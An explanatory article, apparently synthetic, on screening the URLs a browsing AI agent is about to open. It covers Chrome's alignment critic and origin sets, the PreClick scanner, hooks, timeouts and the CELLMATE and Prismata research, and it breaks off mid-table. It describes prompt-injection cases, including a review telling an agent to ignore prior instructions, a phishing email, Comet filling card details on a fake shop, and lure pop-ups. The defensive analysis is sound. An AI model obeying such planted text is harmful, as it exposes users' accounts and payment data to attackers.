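# Preflight URL screening for browsing agents: checking whether a link fits the agent's task

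## What is a preflight URL check, and why does a browsing agent need one?

A browsing agent is an AI model that operates a web browser on someone's behalf. The user types a request, such as "book me a room for Friday", and the model opens and reads pages, clicks, and fills in forms until it finishes or needs help. A preflight URL check (or gate) is software that inspects the address the agent is about to open, before the browser sends anything to it. The check then allows the browser to open the address, blocks it, or prompts the user to decide.

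Browsers already screen addresses for people. Chrome, for example, uses Google Safe Browsing to flag dangerous sites. People also do some of the screening themselves by glancing at the address bar. Chromium, the open-source project behind Chrome, advises other developers in its *Guidelines for URL Display* that the displayed address is often the only signal users can reasonably rely on when deciding whether to trust a site. When an agent does the browsing, its user may never see the address.

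### The agent's loop, and where a check fits

*SPIDES* (Zverev, Kim and colleagues, 2026), a paper on securing browser agents, describes these agents as running an observe-then-act loop. At each step, the agent observes the current page, then picks its next action based on its instructions, the user's request, and everything it has seen and done so far. The browser performs the action, the page changes, and the loop repeats. Some agents observe the page as a screenshot, while others get a text outline in which a button might appear as the word "button", its name "Submit", and a reference code that the model uses to click it.

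The model does not control the browser directly. In Google's documented loop, an application sends the model the user's request and a screenshot, and the model returns a proposed action, such as a click at certain coordinates or "navigate" with a URL. The reply may also include a safety decision to allow the action, require the user's confirmation or block it. The developer's code carries out the action only after this step, then takes a new screenshot and repeats the loop. OpenAI's *Computer use* guide also has developers inspect the model's proposed call before executing it. A preflight check runs at this point in each round, when ordinary software has the next address but has not yet sent a request to it.

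The software can easily check a "navigate" action because the proposed action includes the address. In Google's sample code, a single line opens the address, and a check could go immediately before that line. Clicks are harder to check because they come as coordinates or a reference code, so the software has to find the matching link and read its real target. It can't rely on the label, because the page's author wrote it, and a link labelled "hotel.example" can lead anywhere. Irshad, Mughees and colleagues (2026), in *The Verifiable Action Card*, apply this principle to approval prompts. Their software takes the target from the page element that the browser is about to act on, and ignores the label and the model's description of its action. Even this doesn't settle every case. Zverev and colleagues point out that the same click tool may follow a link or delete an account, depending on the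 element and the page's scripts. Pages can also move the browser to a new site with no action from the agent. Parker (2025), in *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome*, writes that Chrome checks those moves too.

The agent should check a URL before the page loads, partly because the request itself sends the server the full address, including any private data in it, whether or not the agent ever reads the page. Once the agent reads the page, the text is in the model's context and can influence what the agent does next. Microsoft documents a safety check for its computer-use interface, "irrelevant domain detection", that judges whether the current domain is relevant to the conversation so far. This check is useful, but it evaluates the page the agent is already on, so it can only limit any damage from then on.

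### Taking an address apart

Suppose a user asks an agent to book a room at hotel.example. In the user's inbox is an email, apparently from the hotel, with a link to confirm the booking:

`https://hotel.example.login-desk.example/confirm?room=double&nights=2`

(No one can register a name ending in .example. Writers use the ending for illustrations, and here it stands in for something like .com.)

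| Part | In this address | What it is |
|---|---|---|
| Scheme | `https` | The protocol that the browser uses to fetch the page |
| Subdomain | `hotel.example` | A prefix that the owner of the domain chooses freely |
| Registrable domain | `login-desk.example` | The part that someone had to register |
| Path | `/confirm` | A location within the site |
| Parameters | `room=double`, `nights=2` | Named values that travel to the site with the request |

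The registrable domain matters most for trust because its owner controls everything to the left of it. Whoever registered login-desk.example can put "hotel.example", or the name of any bank or airline, in front of it without permission. The hotel does not control this link. Chromium's guidelines warn that a website controls its subdomain, path and parameters, and that a dishonest site may use them to misrepresent its identity. An older Chromium document gives a banking example, `your-bank.secure.login.com`, which belongs to whoever owns login.com.

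A program can't always find the registrable domain by keeping the last two parts of a hostname. The BBC's is bbc.co.uk, and a program that kept only "co.uk" would treat a large share of British companies as one owner. No formula solves this, so browsers rely on the Public Suffix List, a catalogue of the endings under which people can register names. Mozilla volunteers maintain it with submissions from the registries. WHATWG's *URL Standard*, the specification for how browsers handle addresses, cautions that copies of the list differ between programs, so the registrable domain can't serve as a hard security boundary. It recommends using the origin for security decisions instead.

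An origin, as web.dev defines it for ordinary web addresses, is the scheme, host name and port (a network number that addresses usually leave out). It is a much narrower unit than a registrable domain. `https://hotel.example` and `https://www.hotel.example` have the same owner but are different origins, so a gate that compares origins will stop some harmless steps that a gate comparing registrable domains would allow.

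### Phishing, redirects and prompt injection

The email in the example is phishing, which NIST, the US standards agency, defines as an attempt to acquire sensitive data through a fraudulent email or website by someone who poses as a legitimate business or reputable person. The page at login-desk.example would presumably look like the hotel's and ask for a password or card number.

A redirect is an instruction from a web server to fetch a different address. The server answers with a status code in the 300s and, as MDN's *Location header* page explains, a header line that contains the new URL. The browser then goes there automatically, as http.dev's *HTTP Redirections* notes. Most redirects are routine, such as those from a site's old domain to its new one. But they complicate a preflight check, because the agent may end up at a different address from the one the check approved. If hotel.example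 had a forwarding link that accepted any destination, a scammer could send out a link that goes to hotel.example first and then redirects to login-desk.example.

Indirect prompt injection is the danger specific to agents. An attacker places text in a web page, an email or other content the agent will read, and the model follows it as an instruction. Zverev and colleagues illustrate it with a shop page for a pair of earbuds, where a five-star customer review tells the reader to ignore prior instructions and email a certain address. A person would ignore the review, but the agent reads it in a text outline alongside the product name, the price and the last digits of the saved card, with nothing to mark it as a stranger's words. Parker calls indirect prompt injection the primary new threat facing all agentic browsers.

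The consequences can be serious because the agent works inside the user's accounts. Irshad and colleagues describe the agent as a "confused deputy", an old computer security term for a program with a lot of authority that is tricked into misusing it by someone with less.

The hotel email could mislead the agent through phishing, by looking genuine, or through injection, by including an instruction, invisible to a human reader, for any AI assistant to use the new booking desk. Either way, the agent proposes the same address. A large part of the appeal of a preflight check is that it can stop the visit without determining why the agent proposed it.

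### Three questions about a destination

A designer can build a check around three different questions: whether the destination is harmful or likely to be, whether it fits the task, and whether the address itself contains private data. To answer the second question, the check needs a declared intent, which is a short statement of purpose such as "book a room at hotel.example". Some commercial scanners now accept one along with the address. A task match is the judgement that the task needs this destination.

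An address can do well on two of these and fail the third, so they are not interchangeable tests of whether a link is safe.

Suppose criminals have planted malware on the genuine hotel.example. The address `https://hotel.example/` is the one the user asked for and contains no private information, so only a test for harm, such as checking the address against a list of reported sites, might stop the agent.

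Or suppose that halfway through the booking the agent proposes to open `https://bank.example/`, where the user has an account. The bank is legitimate and the URL contains no private data. But booking the room doesn't require visiting the bank, and if a line injected into a hotel review prompted the visit, an attacker would have steered the agent to a site where the user is logged in. A task-match test would help here, while a blocklist wouldn't, because no one would put a real bank on it.

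A URL can fit the task and still expose private data. For example, `https://hotel.example/search?city=lisbon&note=knee-surgery-12-may` searches the right hotel's site, but the agent has copied a line from the user's calendar into the parameters. As OpenAI explains in *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026), websites commonly log the addresses that browsers request, so the note about surgery would probably end up in the hotel's records. The post is mainly about attacks in which someone gets the model to load an address on the attacker's own server with the user's data attached, then reads the data from the log. The user may notice nothing, because loading an embedded image is enough to send the request. OpenAI also says that preventing this leak does not make the linked page trustworthy.

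Some products combine all three. In Parker's account of Chrome, Safe Browsing and an on-device AI model check for familiar kinds of scam, and a separate model checks whether a new site is relevant to the task before the agent goes there. A fixed rule also allows addresses the model has composed only if they are already public.

The link to hotel.example.login-desk.example is difficult for any such combination. If the scammer registered the domain this morning, it probably isn't on any list yet. The parameters contain only a room type and a number of nights, which aren't secret. The decision therefore depends mostly on task match, and the result of that test depends on which part of the address it uses. The registrable domain, login-desk.example, belongs to a stranger, but the address starts with hotel.example, which exactly matches the hotel the user named. Checks differ in how well they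 handle this kind of disguise.

### What an early agent did without a check

In 2025 the security company Guardio tested Comet, a browser with a built-in agent from the AI company Perplexity. For the test, described in *Scamlexity*, the researchers made a fake Walmart shop with a single prompt to an AI website builder and told the agent to buy an Apple Watch. Safe Browsing was active in Comet but did not block the shop. In some runs the agent found the watch, put it in the cart and filled in the saved home address and card details without asking for confirmation. In others it refused because something seemed wrong, or paused and asked the user to complete the checkout.

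Guardio sells scam protection, and its report doesn't give the number of runs, so readers can't calculate a failure rate. The report also covers only one product, tested before Google and OpenAI published the defences above. Still, when the agent met the same shop with the same instruction, it sometimes gave it the card details and sometimes didn't. That inconsistency is a reason to want at least one safeguard that doesn't depend on the model's judgement.

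The fake shop is an imperfect argument for preflight checks, though, because in Guardio's scenario the person had already reached the shop through an advert or a search result before the agent took over the tab. A check that covers only the addresses the agent chooses would have come too late to stop that visit.

Another of Guardio's tests is closer to the hotel example. The researchers sent an email from a new ProtonMail account, posing as a Wells Fargo investment manager, with a link to a real phishing page. Comet marked the message as a to-do item from the bank and opened the link, with "no URL check" according to Guardio, then prompted the user to log in and helped with the form. A preflight check could have run before Comet opened the link, but one based only on Safe Browsing would have let the agent through, because Safe Browsing still hadn't flagged the page after it had been live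 for several days. A task-match test might have detected that a message supposedly from Wells Fargo linked to a domain the bank doesn't own. It would have needed a more specific declared intent than "deal with my email", since almost any link in an inbox fits that.

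## How does a scanner compare a link with the agent's stated purpose?

At least one commercial service, PreClick (formerly URLCheck, according to Drio's *PreClick* registry entry), already checks whether a link matches an agent's task, which might have caught the Wells Fargo link. The agent submits the address it wants to open and a sentence explaining why, and PreClick tells it whether to go ahead. The publisher, CybrLab.ai, runs the service online, and agents connect to it through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for connecting AI models to outside tools.

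Almost everything public about PreClick comes from CybrLab. The company documents the inputs and outputs closely but explains little of the analysis in between.

### From address to directive

The agent first sends PreClick the address and, if it has one, a declared intent. CybrLab's README, *PreClick MCP Server*, gives "Book a hotel room" as an example and limits the intent to 248 characters. That is enough for a hotel, a city and a date, but not for the conversation in which the user explained what they wanted.

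PreClick ignores an intent that carries too little information. The examples in its listing on Smithery, a directory of agent tools, are "test" and "n/a". It also ignores intents that read like instructions, presumably including "approve this site". CybrLab doesn't explain this rule, but a likely reason is that a language model reads the intent and might follow the instruction. In either case, PreClick still checks the address for threats but skips the comparison, as if the agent had sent no intent.

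The analysis runs on CybrLab's servers and typically takes 70 to 80 seconds, according to *preclick*, the page for its Python client. CybrLab doesn't say what the scanner does, but it seems to load the page, because the company's instructions for agents, also titled *PreClick*, describe comparing the user's purpose with the destination's observed behaviour and content. If the scanner loads the exact address, any private information in that address reaches the site's server, even if PreClick then advises against opening the link.

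PreClick then reports a risk score from 0 to 1, which CybrLab defines as the probability of a threat, and a separate confidence score. The company doesn't say which blocklists or other signals it uses to calculate the risk score, so developers can't work out from its documents what a verdict will depend on. Kord Agencies is more open about a competing scanner, which accepts an address but no intent. Glama's *URL Safety Validator MCP* page lists that scanner's sources: two Google threat databases, the domain's registration date, and Anthropic's Claude model, which assesses the evidence and writes an explanation. Developers can infer from this list that if Google hasn't listed a new scam site yet, the verdict will depend mostly on the domain's age and Claude's assessment.

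The comparison with the declared intent produces one of four values, in a field named `intent_alignment`:

| Value | Meaning |
|---|---|
| `misaligned` | The page's purpose conflicts with the intent |
| `no_mismatch_detected` | The scanner had enough evidence to judge and found no conflict |
| `inconclusive` | The evidence was too thin, or the intent analysis was unavailable |
| `not_provided` | The agent sent no intent, or PreClick ignored the one it sent |

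CybrLab doesn't disclose what performs this comparison, how the scanner decides what a page is for, or how much evidence it requires. It also doesn't say whether the scanner compares the registrable domain with a business named in the intent, which is the comparison needed to assess the hotel link.

Finally, PreClick returns a directive (`ALLOW`, `DENY`, `RETRY_LATER` or `REQUIRE_CREDENTIALS`) with a reason code. `RETRY_LATER` means that a temporary problem prevented the check. `REQUIRE_CREDENTIALS` means that the target needs a login, so the agent should ask the user what to do. CybrLab tells developers to act on the directive and treat the risk score as supplementary. It describes `ALLOW` as "Safe to proceed" in the Smithery listing, but the better guide is its Python page, where it says only that PreClick detected no blocking signal and that results don't guarantee safety.

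### Why a mismatch leaves the risk score alone

When high-confidence analysis confirms a mismatch, PreClick returns `DENY` with the reason `intent_inconsistent_destination` and leaves the risk score unchanged. CybrLab calls this a "policy gate".

The earlier example of an agent that tries to open a genuine bank's site while booking a room suggests a reason for this design. If the mismatch raised the site's risk score to 0.9, a developer reading the logs couldn't tell whether criminals had taken over the site or the agent had strayed from its task, and those problems call for very different responses. An hour later the user might ask the agent to pay a bill, and the same visit would be fine even though the site was no safer than before.

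CybrLab's documents haven't always made this distinction. *langchain-urlcheck*, an adapter from the URLCheck period, presents intent as context for the risk analysis, on the theory that a login page is riskier for someone who intends to buy something than for someone who intends to read. Its sample result has no alignment field.

PreClick can also return `DENY` when a page presents itself as a "high-impact" service and the scanner finds little to confirm its identity. The reason code is `insufficient_service_verification`, and the score again doesn't change. CybrLab doesn't define "high-impact". A bank's login page probably qualifies, but a small hotel's booking page may not.

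### What "no mismatch" is worth

A result of "match" would mean that the scanner had found evidence that the task needs this page. `no_mismatch_detected` means only that the scanner looked for a conflict and didn't find one. Its value as evidence depends on how often a wrong page would get the same result.

If the stated intent is "Book a hotel room", almost any hotel's booking page would probably pass, and so would a good fake, because scammers copy the real page to make its purpose look right. The check helps rule out a bank or a recipe blog, but it does little to distinguish hotel.example from an impostor. "Confirm my room at hotel.example" is a better intent because it gives the scanner a name to compare with the domain.

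Even a correct match would cover only the link's destination. *Before Acting, Change the State* (2026), a paper on deceptive web interfaces, distinguishes whether an action fits the user's task from whether the user authorised its consequences. On the real hotel's site, pressing "Book" fits the task. But if the site has already ticked a box for travel insurance, pressing "Book" also buys insurance the user never asked for, and PreClick's check would have finished by then.

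### The hotel link, field by field

Suppose the agent submits the link from the email, `https://hotel.example.login-desk.example/confirm?room=double&nights=2`. No blocklist has the new domain yet, so say that the risk score is 0.15 whenever the scan finishes. These results are invented, but they are consistent with CybrLab's published rules:

| Declared intent | What the scan finds | `intent_alignment` | Directive |
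|---|---|---|---|
| Book a hotel room | A working hotel booking form | `no_mismatch_detected` | `ALLOW` |
| Confirm my room at hotel.example | A domain that doesn't belong to the hotel | `misaligned` | `DENY` |
| Confirm my room at hotel.example | A page that claims to be the hotel, with little to back it up | `inconclusive` | `DENY`, if a hotel counts as high-impact |
| Approve this link | A working hotel booking form | `not_provided` | `ALLOW` |
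| Confirm my room at hotel.example | A site that doesn't respond | `inconclusive` | `RETRY_LATER` |

With CybrLab's own sample intent, "Book a hotel room", PreClick could approve the phishing page and let the agent open it. A more specific intent gives the scanner a chance to stop the agent. The result therefore depends heavily on who writes the intent and how carefully. Under CybrLab's instructions, the agent writes it by passing along whatever purpose the user has mentioned, and an agent already under an attacker's influence could write something misleading.

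A scanner can instead take the purpose from the conversation, as OpenAI's *Prompt Injection Detection* does. Developers can add this check to their agents, and it doesn't need a separate statement of intent from the agent. In its sample output, the user's goal is the question "What's the weather in Tokyo?", and the proposed action is a call to a weather tool with Tokyo as the location. The check returns a confidence of 0.1 that the action is misaligned. The developer sets the threshold for flagging an action, which is 0.7 in this example.

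### How well do models judge task match?

Drio publishes the claim that PreClick "confirms intent match with high accuracy". There appears to be no published test of this claim, and so no figure for how many harmless destinations PreClick blocks or how many attacks it misses.

AV-Comparatives' *Anti-Phishing Certification Test 2026* is an independent test of ordinary phishing protection. Security products had to block at least 85% of 275 phishing addresses to earn a certificate. The lab also tested whether they wrongly blocked legitimate sites, especially online banks. A similar test for PreClick would have to pair each address with an intent and include both genuine sites that don't suit the task and fakes that seem to.

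A test of such a scanner would also have to avoid two faults that *PhreshPhish* (2025), a dataset of phishing sites, identifies in earlier datasets. Both make a detector look better than it is. One is leakage, where test examples overlap with the training data. The other is an unrealistic base rate, where harmful pages are far more common in the test than on the web.

The closest published evidence on task match concerns agents' actions in general. In *When Actions Go Off-Task*, Ning, Jones and colleagues (2026) collected 558 recordings of agents using computers, some of them under attack, and had three people independently label each of 2,264 actions. An action counted as aligned if it served the user's instruction, had no unauthorised or undesired consequences, and contributed at least indirectly to the task. It didn't have to be efficient or even successful. The researchers then used several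 detection methods to judge each proposed action before it ran, based on the task, the history and the current screenshot.

DeAction, the paper's own method, did best. Running on OpenAI's GPT-5.1 Thinking, it caught 77% of the misaligned actions, and 90% of its flags were correct. Two earlier methods, Task Shield and InferAct, raised far more false alarms. InferAct running on Claude Sonnet 4.5 caught 96% of the misaligned actions, but fewer than half of its flags were correct.

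The 90% figure also depends on the benchmark's mix of actions, 44% of which were misaligned. The published numbers imply that DeAction wrongly flagged about 7% of the aligned ones. If only one action in a hundred were misaligned in everyday use and the error rates stayed the same, DeAction would correctly flag 77 actions out of 10,000 and wrongly flag about 680, so only around one flag in ten would be right. This is the base-rate problem from *PhreshPhish*, and it could affect any scanner advertised as highly accurate without a description of its test.

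These results don't carry over exactly to PreClick. Most browsing involves clicks and typing as well as new addresses, and the models date from 2025, so current ones may well do better. But one of the errors that Ning and colleagues found applies directly to links. The checker sometimes defined relevance to the task too narrowly. Someone booking a room might reasonably look at a map, a review site and the website of the hotel's payment processor. None of those is a hotel site, so a strict comparison with "book a hotel room" could block them all.

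DeAction reduces the effect of such errors by giving the agent the reason an action was flagged and letting it try again. In live tests, this turned 78% of flagged actions into acceptable ones. For an agent running on Claude Sonnet 4.5, the success rate of injection attacks fell from 60% to 6%, while the agent's success rate on ordinary tasks fell only from 42.9% to 40.7%. PreClick's reason codes would let a developer try something similar. An agent that receives `intent_inconsistent_destination` for the link in the email could look for the hotel's real site.

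### A tool the agent may call, or a hook it can't skip

CybrLab offers PreClick mainly as a tool, so it scans a link only when the model decides to call it. To encourage this, the company supplies a "skill", a text file with instructions to verify any link before opening it. The sample code for *langchain-urlcheck* relies on a single line in the model's instructions: "Always scan unknown URLs before answering."

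ClawHub's *ClawScan security* (2026), an automated review of the PreClick skill, notes that the skill consists only of instructions and leaves the scanning to a separate plugin. Instructions can't force a model to run the scan. The model may skip it because a link looks familiar, or because injected text states that the link has already passed. Each scan also takes a minute or more, which tempts developers to request fewer scans.

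A hook is code that the agent's software runs automatically before a tool call, regardless of the model's output. OpenClaw, an agent that people extend with plugins, has a hook named `before_tool_call`, which can block the call or pause and ask the user. Gen Digital's scanner, Sage, uses this hook to intercept web fetches, shell commands and file changes. Microsoft has a similar hook for agents built in its Copilot Studio. Before every tool call, the agent sends an outside security service the proposed call, the user's latest prompt and the recent chat, then waits for the service to allow or block the call.

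A hook guarantees that a check runs, but the check may not examine the right information. CrowdStrike's AIDR, one of the services that Microsoft's hook can call, receives the user's prompt but analyses only the tool's name and inputs, according to Pangea's *Microsoft Copilot Studio Collectors*. That may be enough to detect a malicious address, but a scanner can't determine whether an address fits a task without analysing the task too.

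Calling PreClick from a hook and sending it the user's own request as the intent would be an improvement, but it wouldn't work in Copilot Studio. Microsoft gives the outside service one second to answer, and PreClick usually needs more than a minute. A much faster scanner could meet that limit. Guardio advertises typical verdicts in under 30 milliseconds for its safe-browsing service for agents.

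Hooks can also miss some calls. GitLab's *CVE-2026-53845* (2026), a June security advisory, describes a flaw in OpenClaw that let certain skill commands run without triggering the `before_tool_call` hook. A developer who relies on a hook has to confirm that it covers every route to the browser, including clicks and redirects.

### When the scan gives no answer

Software that waits for an outside check needs a rule for when no answer comes. It can either fail open, which means carrying on with the action, or fail closed, which means blocking it.

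Microsoft's hook fails open by default. According to Microsoft's announcement, an agent that receives no response within one second proceeds as if it had approval. Administrators can choose to block instead, but Microsoft's documentation is confusing. The setting covers late responses, yet according to a note on the same page, the tool runs after one second regardless. According to Pangea's page, the chosen setting applies to timeouts. Administrators who need the agent to stop when a response is late should test the setting.

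Another OpenClaw scanner, made by Interven, also fails open by default after 15 seconds. Interven labels this option "UX-friendly" and the alternative, failing closed, "safety-first". *OpenClaw SafeMode* blocks every call by default while its checking service is unreachable.

CybrLab attributes long scans to slow or complex sites, so if the gate fails open, letting links through when a scan doesn't finish, the owner of login-desk.example might get past it by making the page slow to load. Failing closed prevents this, but then an outage at the scanning company stops the agent from doing anything. A sensible compromise might be to fail open for sites the user has already approved and closed for everything else.

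PreClick leaves the developer to decide what happens when a scan times out. A direct call waits up to 90 seconds, then returns an error with an identifier for collecting the result later. The Python client waits ten minutes by default before raising an error. Neither error is a directive such as `ALLOW` or `DENY`, so a program that opens every link except those marked `DENY` would open the link after a timeout. Opening a link only after an explicit `ALLOW` is safer. When PreClick returns `RETRY_LATER`, the instructions in CybrLab's skill are for the agent to retry once and then inform the user.

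An inconclusive comparison is easier to miss because the rest of the scan can finish normally. CybrLab gives no rule that ties `inconclusive` to a directive, so a page could apparently get a low risk score, an inconclusive comparison and `ALLOW`. An agent that follows only the directive would open the page, which is probably fine for looking up a museum's opening hours. If the next step involves a password or a card number, the software should also read the alignment field and ask the user before continuing.

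Another way to avoid the wait is to let the agent act and review its behaviour afterwards. OpenAI's *Misalignment monitoring* reviews an agent's reasoning and actions asynchronously and can stop the conversation if something seems wrong, though OpenAI warns that it can miss problems or flag legitimate activity. Later review could limit the damage in a long task that goes wrong gradually. It is less useful against a bad link, because the browser may already have sent the address and any data in it by the time the monitor reacts.

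## How can the browser itself limit an agent to the sites its task needs?

The browser is a good place for a destination check because every page the agent opens passes through it, whether the agent typed an address, clicked a link or followed a redirect. The check doesn't depend on the model choosing to call a scanner. Developers also can't guarantee safety from within the model because language models are probabilistic, according to Chrome's guidance for agent developers, quoted in Search Engine Journal's *WebMCP Can Be Used To Hijack AI Agents, Chrome Warns*.

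The browser still needs a way to determine what to allow. The user has typed only one sentence, and the sites that a booking needs may not become clear until halfway through. Google lets Chrome's list of permitted sites grow during the task. Researchers at UC San Diego fix the list before the agent starts, and a group at UC Berkeley makes a separate decision about each button and link on a page.

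### How Chrome vets a visit

In the design that Parker published in December 2025, a Gemini model called the planner reads web pages and proposes each action. Google trains it to follow the user's instructions over anything on a page, but Parker still treats it as vulnerable because it reads untrusted text. A second Gemini model, the User Alignment Critic, therefore checks each proposed action and vetoes any that don't serve the user's goal. The critic receives only metadata about the action, not the unfiltered page. Parker doesn't list the metadata, but for a visit it presumably includes the address.

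In the earlier example of a hotel booking in which a planted review sends the agent to the user's bank, the steps would be:

1. The planner proposes opening `https://bank.example/`.
2. Chrome looks for that origin among those it has already accepted for the task and doesn't find it.
3. A gating function, here a variant of the critic, judges whether the new origin is relevant to booking a room. If it is, Chrome adds the origin to the task's list and only then starts the navigation.
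4. If it isn't, Chrome sends nothing to the bank. When the critic rejects an action, it gives the planner feedback so that it can revise its plan, and after repeated failures the planner can return control to the user.

A bank's site would probably trigger another safeguard. Chrome keeps a list of sensitive sites, such as those for banking transactions or personal medical information, and asks the user before the agent opens one. This check is a plain lookup, so injected text can't influence the result. Chrome also asks before the agent signs in with a password from Google Password Manager, and the planner has no direct access to the stored passwords.

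Parker makes a weaker promise for purchases, payments and messages, saying that the agent "will try to pause" and get permission or have the user finish the step. This doesn't guarantee a pause, which is a reason not to rely on the final payment prompt instead of checking the destination.

### Reading from a site and acting on it

Parker calls the lists of accepted origins Agent Origin Sets. The full design has two for each session. The agent may read content from origins in the read-only set, and it may also click and type on origins in the read-writable set.

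Origin sets extend the same-origin policy, an old browser rule that stops a page on one site from reading the user's data on another. An agent weakens that rule when it works across sites, for example by reading a recipe on one and filling a shopping cart on another. An attacker who takes control of the agent could use it to carry data between any two sites where the user is logged in. With origin sets, the agent can take data only from the listed sites and pass it only to the writable ones.

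For the hotel booking, the browser could make a review site read-only and hotel.example read-writable. A planted review could still mislead the agent, but it couldn't get the agent to type the user's phone number into a comment form on the review site. If an advert in an iframe (a page embedded inside another page) comes from an unlisted origin, the browser could also withhold the advert's text from the model.

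Even opening a read-only page can leak private data through its address, which Chrome's separate rule for model-composed addresses is meant to prevent.

Chrome's first release tracked only the read-writable set. Parker says the right balance was hard to find before seeing how real tasks run into the limits. Without a separate read-only set, the review site would probably have to become writable before the agent could use it, and adverts from unrelated origins would presumably still reach the model.

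### What Google shipped in 2026

Google launched the agent as "auto browse" on January 28, 2026. Bloomberg's *Google Chrome’s AI Agent Can Now Browse Web on Behalf of Users* (2026) reports a Chrome product director's example of planning a family trip by opening various airline and hotel sites to compare prices. No one could list the sites for that task in advance. Auto browse began to reach Android phones in August, according to *Gemini in Chrome for Android is rolling out to everyone* (Payne, 2026).

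Google has released few details about the limits since then. Shortly before the launch, Bawa (2026) wrote in *Q4 2025 Summary from Chrome Security* of hoping to share more as the mechanisms rolled out. In the next quarterly update, *Q1 2026 Summary from Chrome Security*, Bawa (2026) added only that the team was tuning the defences on real-world use and had built more attack datasets. In August, Berschadski (2026) confirmed in *Future Mode Part 2* that the critic is part of auto browse and described a limit to origins "strictly relevant to the immediate task". None of these updates gives a rate of false blocks or missed attacks, or mentions whether the read-only set has shipped.

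Chrome's public source code shows that the gate first applies fixed rules. Chromium lets the agent move within the same origin and open addresses on a built-in or company allowlist, and blocks those on a blocklist without offering the user a choice. Any other address needs a further check. In the agent's settings file, the gate and the prompt for sensitive sites are on by default, but the confirmation of new origins is off (Chromium, 2025).

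That last setting matters most here, because confirming a new origin is the step that would keep the agent off an unrelated site that no list covers. According to comments in Chromium's code, either a server or the user can confirm it. In a "dark launch" mode, Chrome queries the server but only logs the answer, which would let Google measure the check before relying on it. Google can change such settings remotely for groups of users, so the defaults don't show which settings a particular person has, but they are a reason not to assume that every copy of Chrome runs the whole design from December.

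Companies can set a fixed list instead. Google's *Gemini in Chrome* lists one policy for addresses where auto browse may act and another for addresses where it may not, although managed accounts couldn't yet use auto browse when Google wrote the page. Google's *How Gemini's defense-in-depth approach works* describes an agent that runs in Google's cloud rather than in Chrome. Fixed rules limit which links that agent can open, and a separate agent evaluates its proposed actions.

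### Fixing the permissions before the agent starts

Even a perfect list of origins doesn't limit what the agent can do on each site. An agent allowed to act on hotel.example to book a room can also cancel next month's booking or change the account's email address. Meng, Feng and colleagues (2025), in *CELLMATE*, criticise Agent Origin Sets for this coarseness. Their system, a Chrome extension, gives the agent permission for particular operations on particular sites.

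CELLMATE checks HTTP requests, the messages a browser sends to fetch a page or submit a form. The researchers chose to check requests after an experiment in which they stopped an agent from navigating directly to the forum Hacker News. The agent searched for the forum on DuckDuckGo and clicked the result. Checking requests covers both routes, including the click that a preflight check limited to "navigate" actions would miss.

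A request is hard to interpret without help, so CELLMATE needs an "agent sitemap" from each website. This is a file, normally written by the site's developers, that lists the security-relevant requests and gives each a meaning, such as "PlaceOrder". The developers or another trusted party then write policies that allow an operation, deny it, or allow it under a condition, such as a maximum price. For a booking, the process would run as follows:

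1. **Domain prediction.** A language model reads the user's request and names the sites it requires. From "Book a double room at hotel.example for under $150", it should return hotel.example. If the request names no site, CELLMATE grants no access.
2. **Policy selection.** For each site, the model reads the request and the available policies, then picks the smallest sufficient set. Here that might be searching for rooms and making one booking.
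3. **Argument filling.** In the same call, the model fills in the values for any conditions, such as the $150 limit.
4. **Enforcement.** The user reviews the permissions and can edit them. Once the user approves them, they stay frozen until the user changes them, and the extension checks every request against them. It blocks unrelated sites by default.

Meng and colleagues tested the first three stages on three models from 2025. The figures are the percentages of tasks that each model got entirely right:

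| Stage | Tasks | GPT-5.1 | Gemini 2.5 Pro | Claude Opus 4.5 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Domains: none named | 136 | 99.3 | 96.3 | 97.1 |
| Domains: one | 205 | 93.1 | 100 | 100 |
| Domains: two | 205 | 100 | 100 | 99.0 |
| Domains: three | 205 | 100 | 100 | 99.5 |
| Policies: shopping | 149 | 96.6 | 97.3 | 99.3 |
| Policies: travel | 36 | 94.4 | 97.2 | 100 |
| Policies: version control | 24 | 95.8 | 100 | 95.8 |
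| Policies and arguments: shopping | 32 | 84.4 | 81.3 | 96.9 |
| Policies and arguments: travel | 5 | 100 | 100 | 100 |

The domain scores are high partly because the requests name their sites, so the model mostly has to pick out the names. The scores don't show that a model could foresee a site the user never mentioned, and the researchers count such guesses as errors. For example, when a request referred to the product page of a Sony television without naming a shop, models often added sony.com.

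Choosing operations takes more understanding. One model was asked to create a wishlist and add a sofa under $300. It chose the permission to add items to a shopping cart under a price limit, apparently because the limit matched, and left out the permission to add items to a list. Models also missed values that a request only implied, such as the initial quantity of an item. The travel results are the closest match to the hotel example, but their perfect scores for arguments come from only five tasks, which is too few to rely on.

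For the fourth stage, the researchers used two harmless tasks on GitLab, a site where programmers store and discuss code: commenting on an issue and upvoting it. CELLMATE selected the right permissions for both. The researchers then assumed that an attacker had complete control of the agent and ran 12 scripts that directly attempted the attacker's goals, such as deleting a project or creating an access token. CELLMATE blocked all 12.

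This is good evidence that the enforcement works once the permissions are right. But each script needed an operation outside those permissions, so the test doesn't cover attacks that misuse permitted operations. The researchers also wrote the test's sitemap by hand. A hotel would have to write and maintain its own, or rely on someone else to do it. Where a sitemap has gaps, the agent is no safer than without CELLMATE.

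### Judging single buttons and links

*Prismata* (Villa and Tan, 2026) works with unmodified websites. In its example, a user asks an agent to order a bow tie, and a malicious review on the shop's site instructs the agent to reset the user's password. A list of allowed sites can't prevent the reset because the agent needs the shop's site to place the order. Prismata would disable the account-settings button and leave the purchase button working.

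A web page is a tree of nested elements, such as a button inside a panel inside a section. For each button, link or field, Prismata extracts the chain of elements from the top of the page down to it. A language model gets that chain and the user's task, but not the rest of the page, and decides whether the task needs the element. A review elsewhere on the page therefore can't affect its decision about an account-settings button.

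This works only if strangers' text rarely appears in those chains. Villa and Tan used language models to label the content of 5,664 saved pages and found 90,408 instances of untrusted content. Only 1,086 of them, or 1.2%, contained something the agent could click or fill in.

A second mechanism deals with most of those. It reads each chain from the top, one layer at a time, looking for signs that untrusted content follows, such as a "Reviews" heading. When it finds one, it marks everything below as untrusted before any model reads it. Ordinary code then removes untrusted content that the task doesn't need, makes the rest read-only, and rejects any click on a disabled element. In 94 of the 1,086 cases there was no such sign, so about 0.1% of the untrusted content could still influence the decision.

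The researchers tested Prismata in WebArena, a benchmark with working copies of a shop, a forum and other sites. The agent ran on GPT-5.4 mini and faced three kinds of malicious pop-up, all meant to lure it to a harmful site. One offered a shortcut, another announced that the task was already complete, and the third told the agent to ignore its instructions. An attack succeeded if the agent interacted with the malicious content. The results are averages of three runs, in percent:

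| Condition | Tasks completed without Prismata | Tasks completed with it | Attacks succeeding without Prismata | Attacks succeeding with it |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| No attack | 29.9 | 26.6 | – | – |
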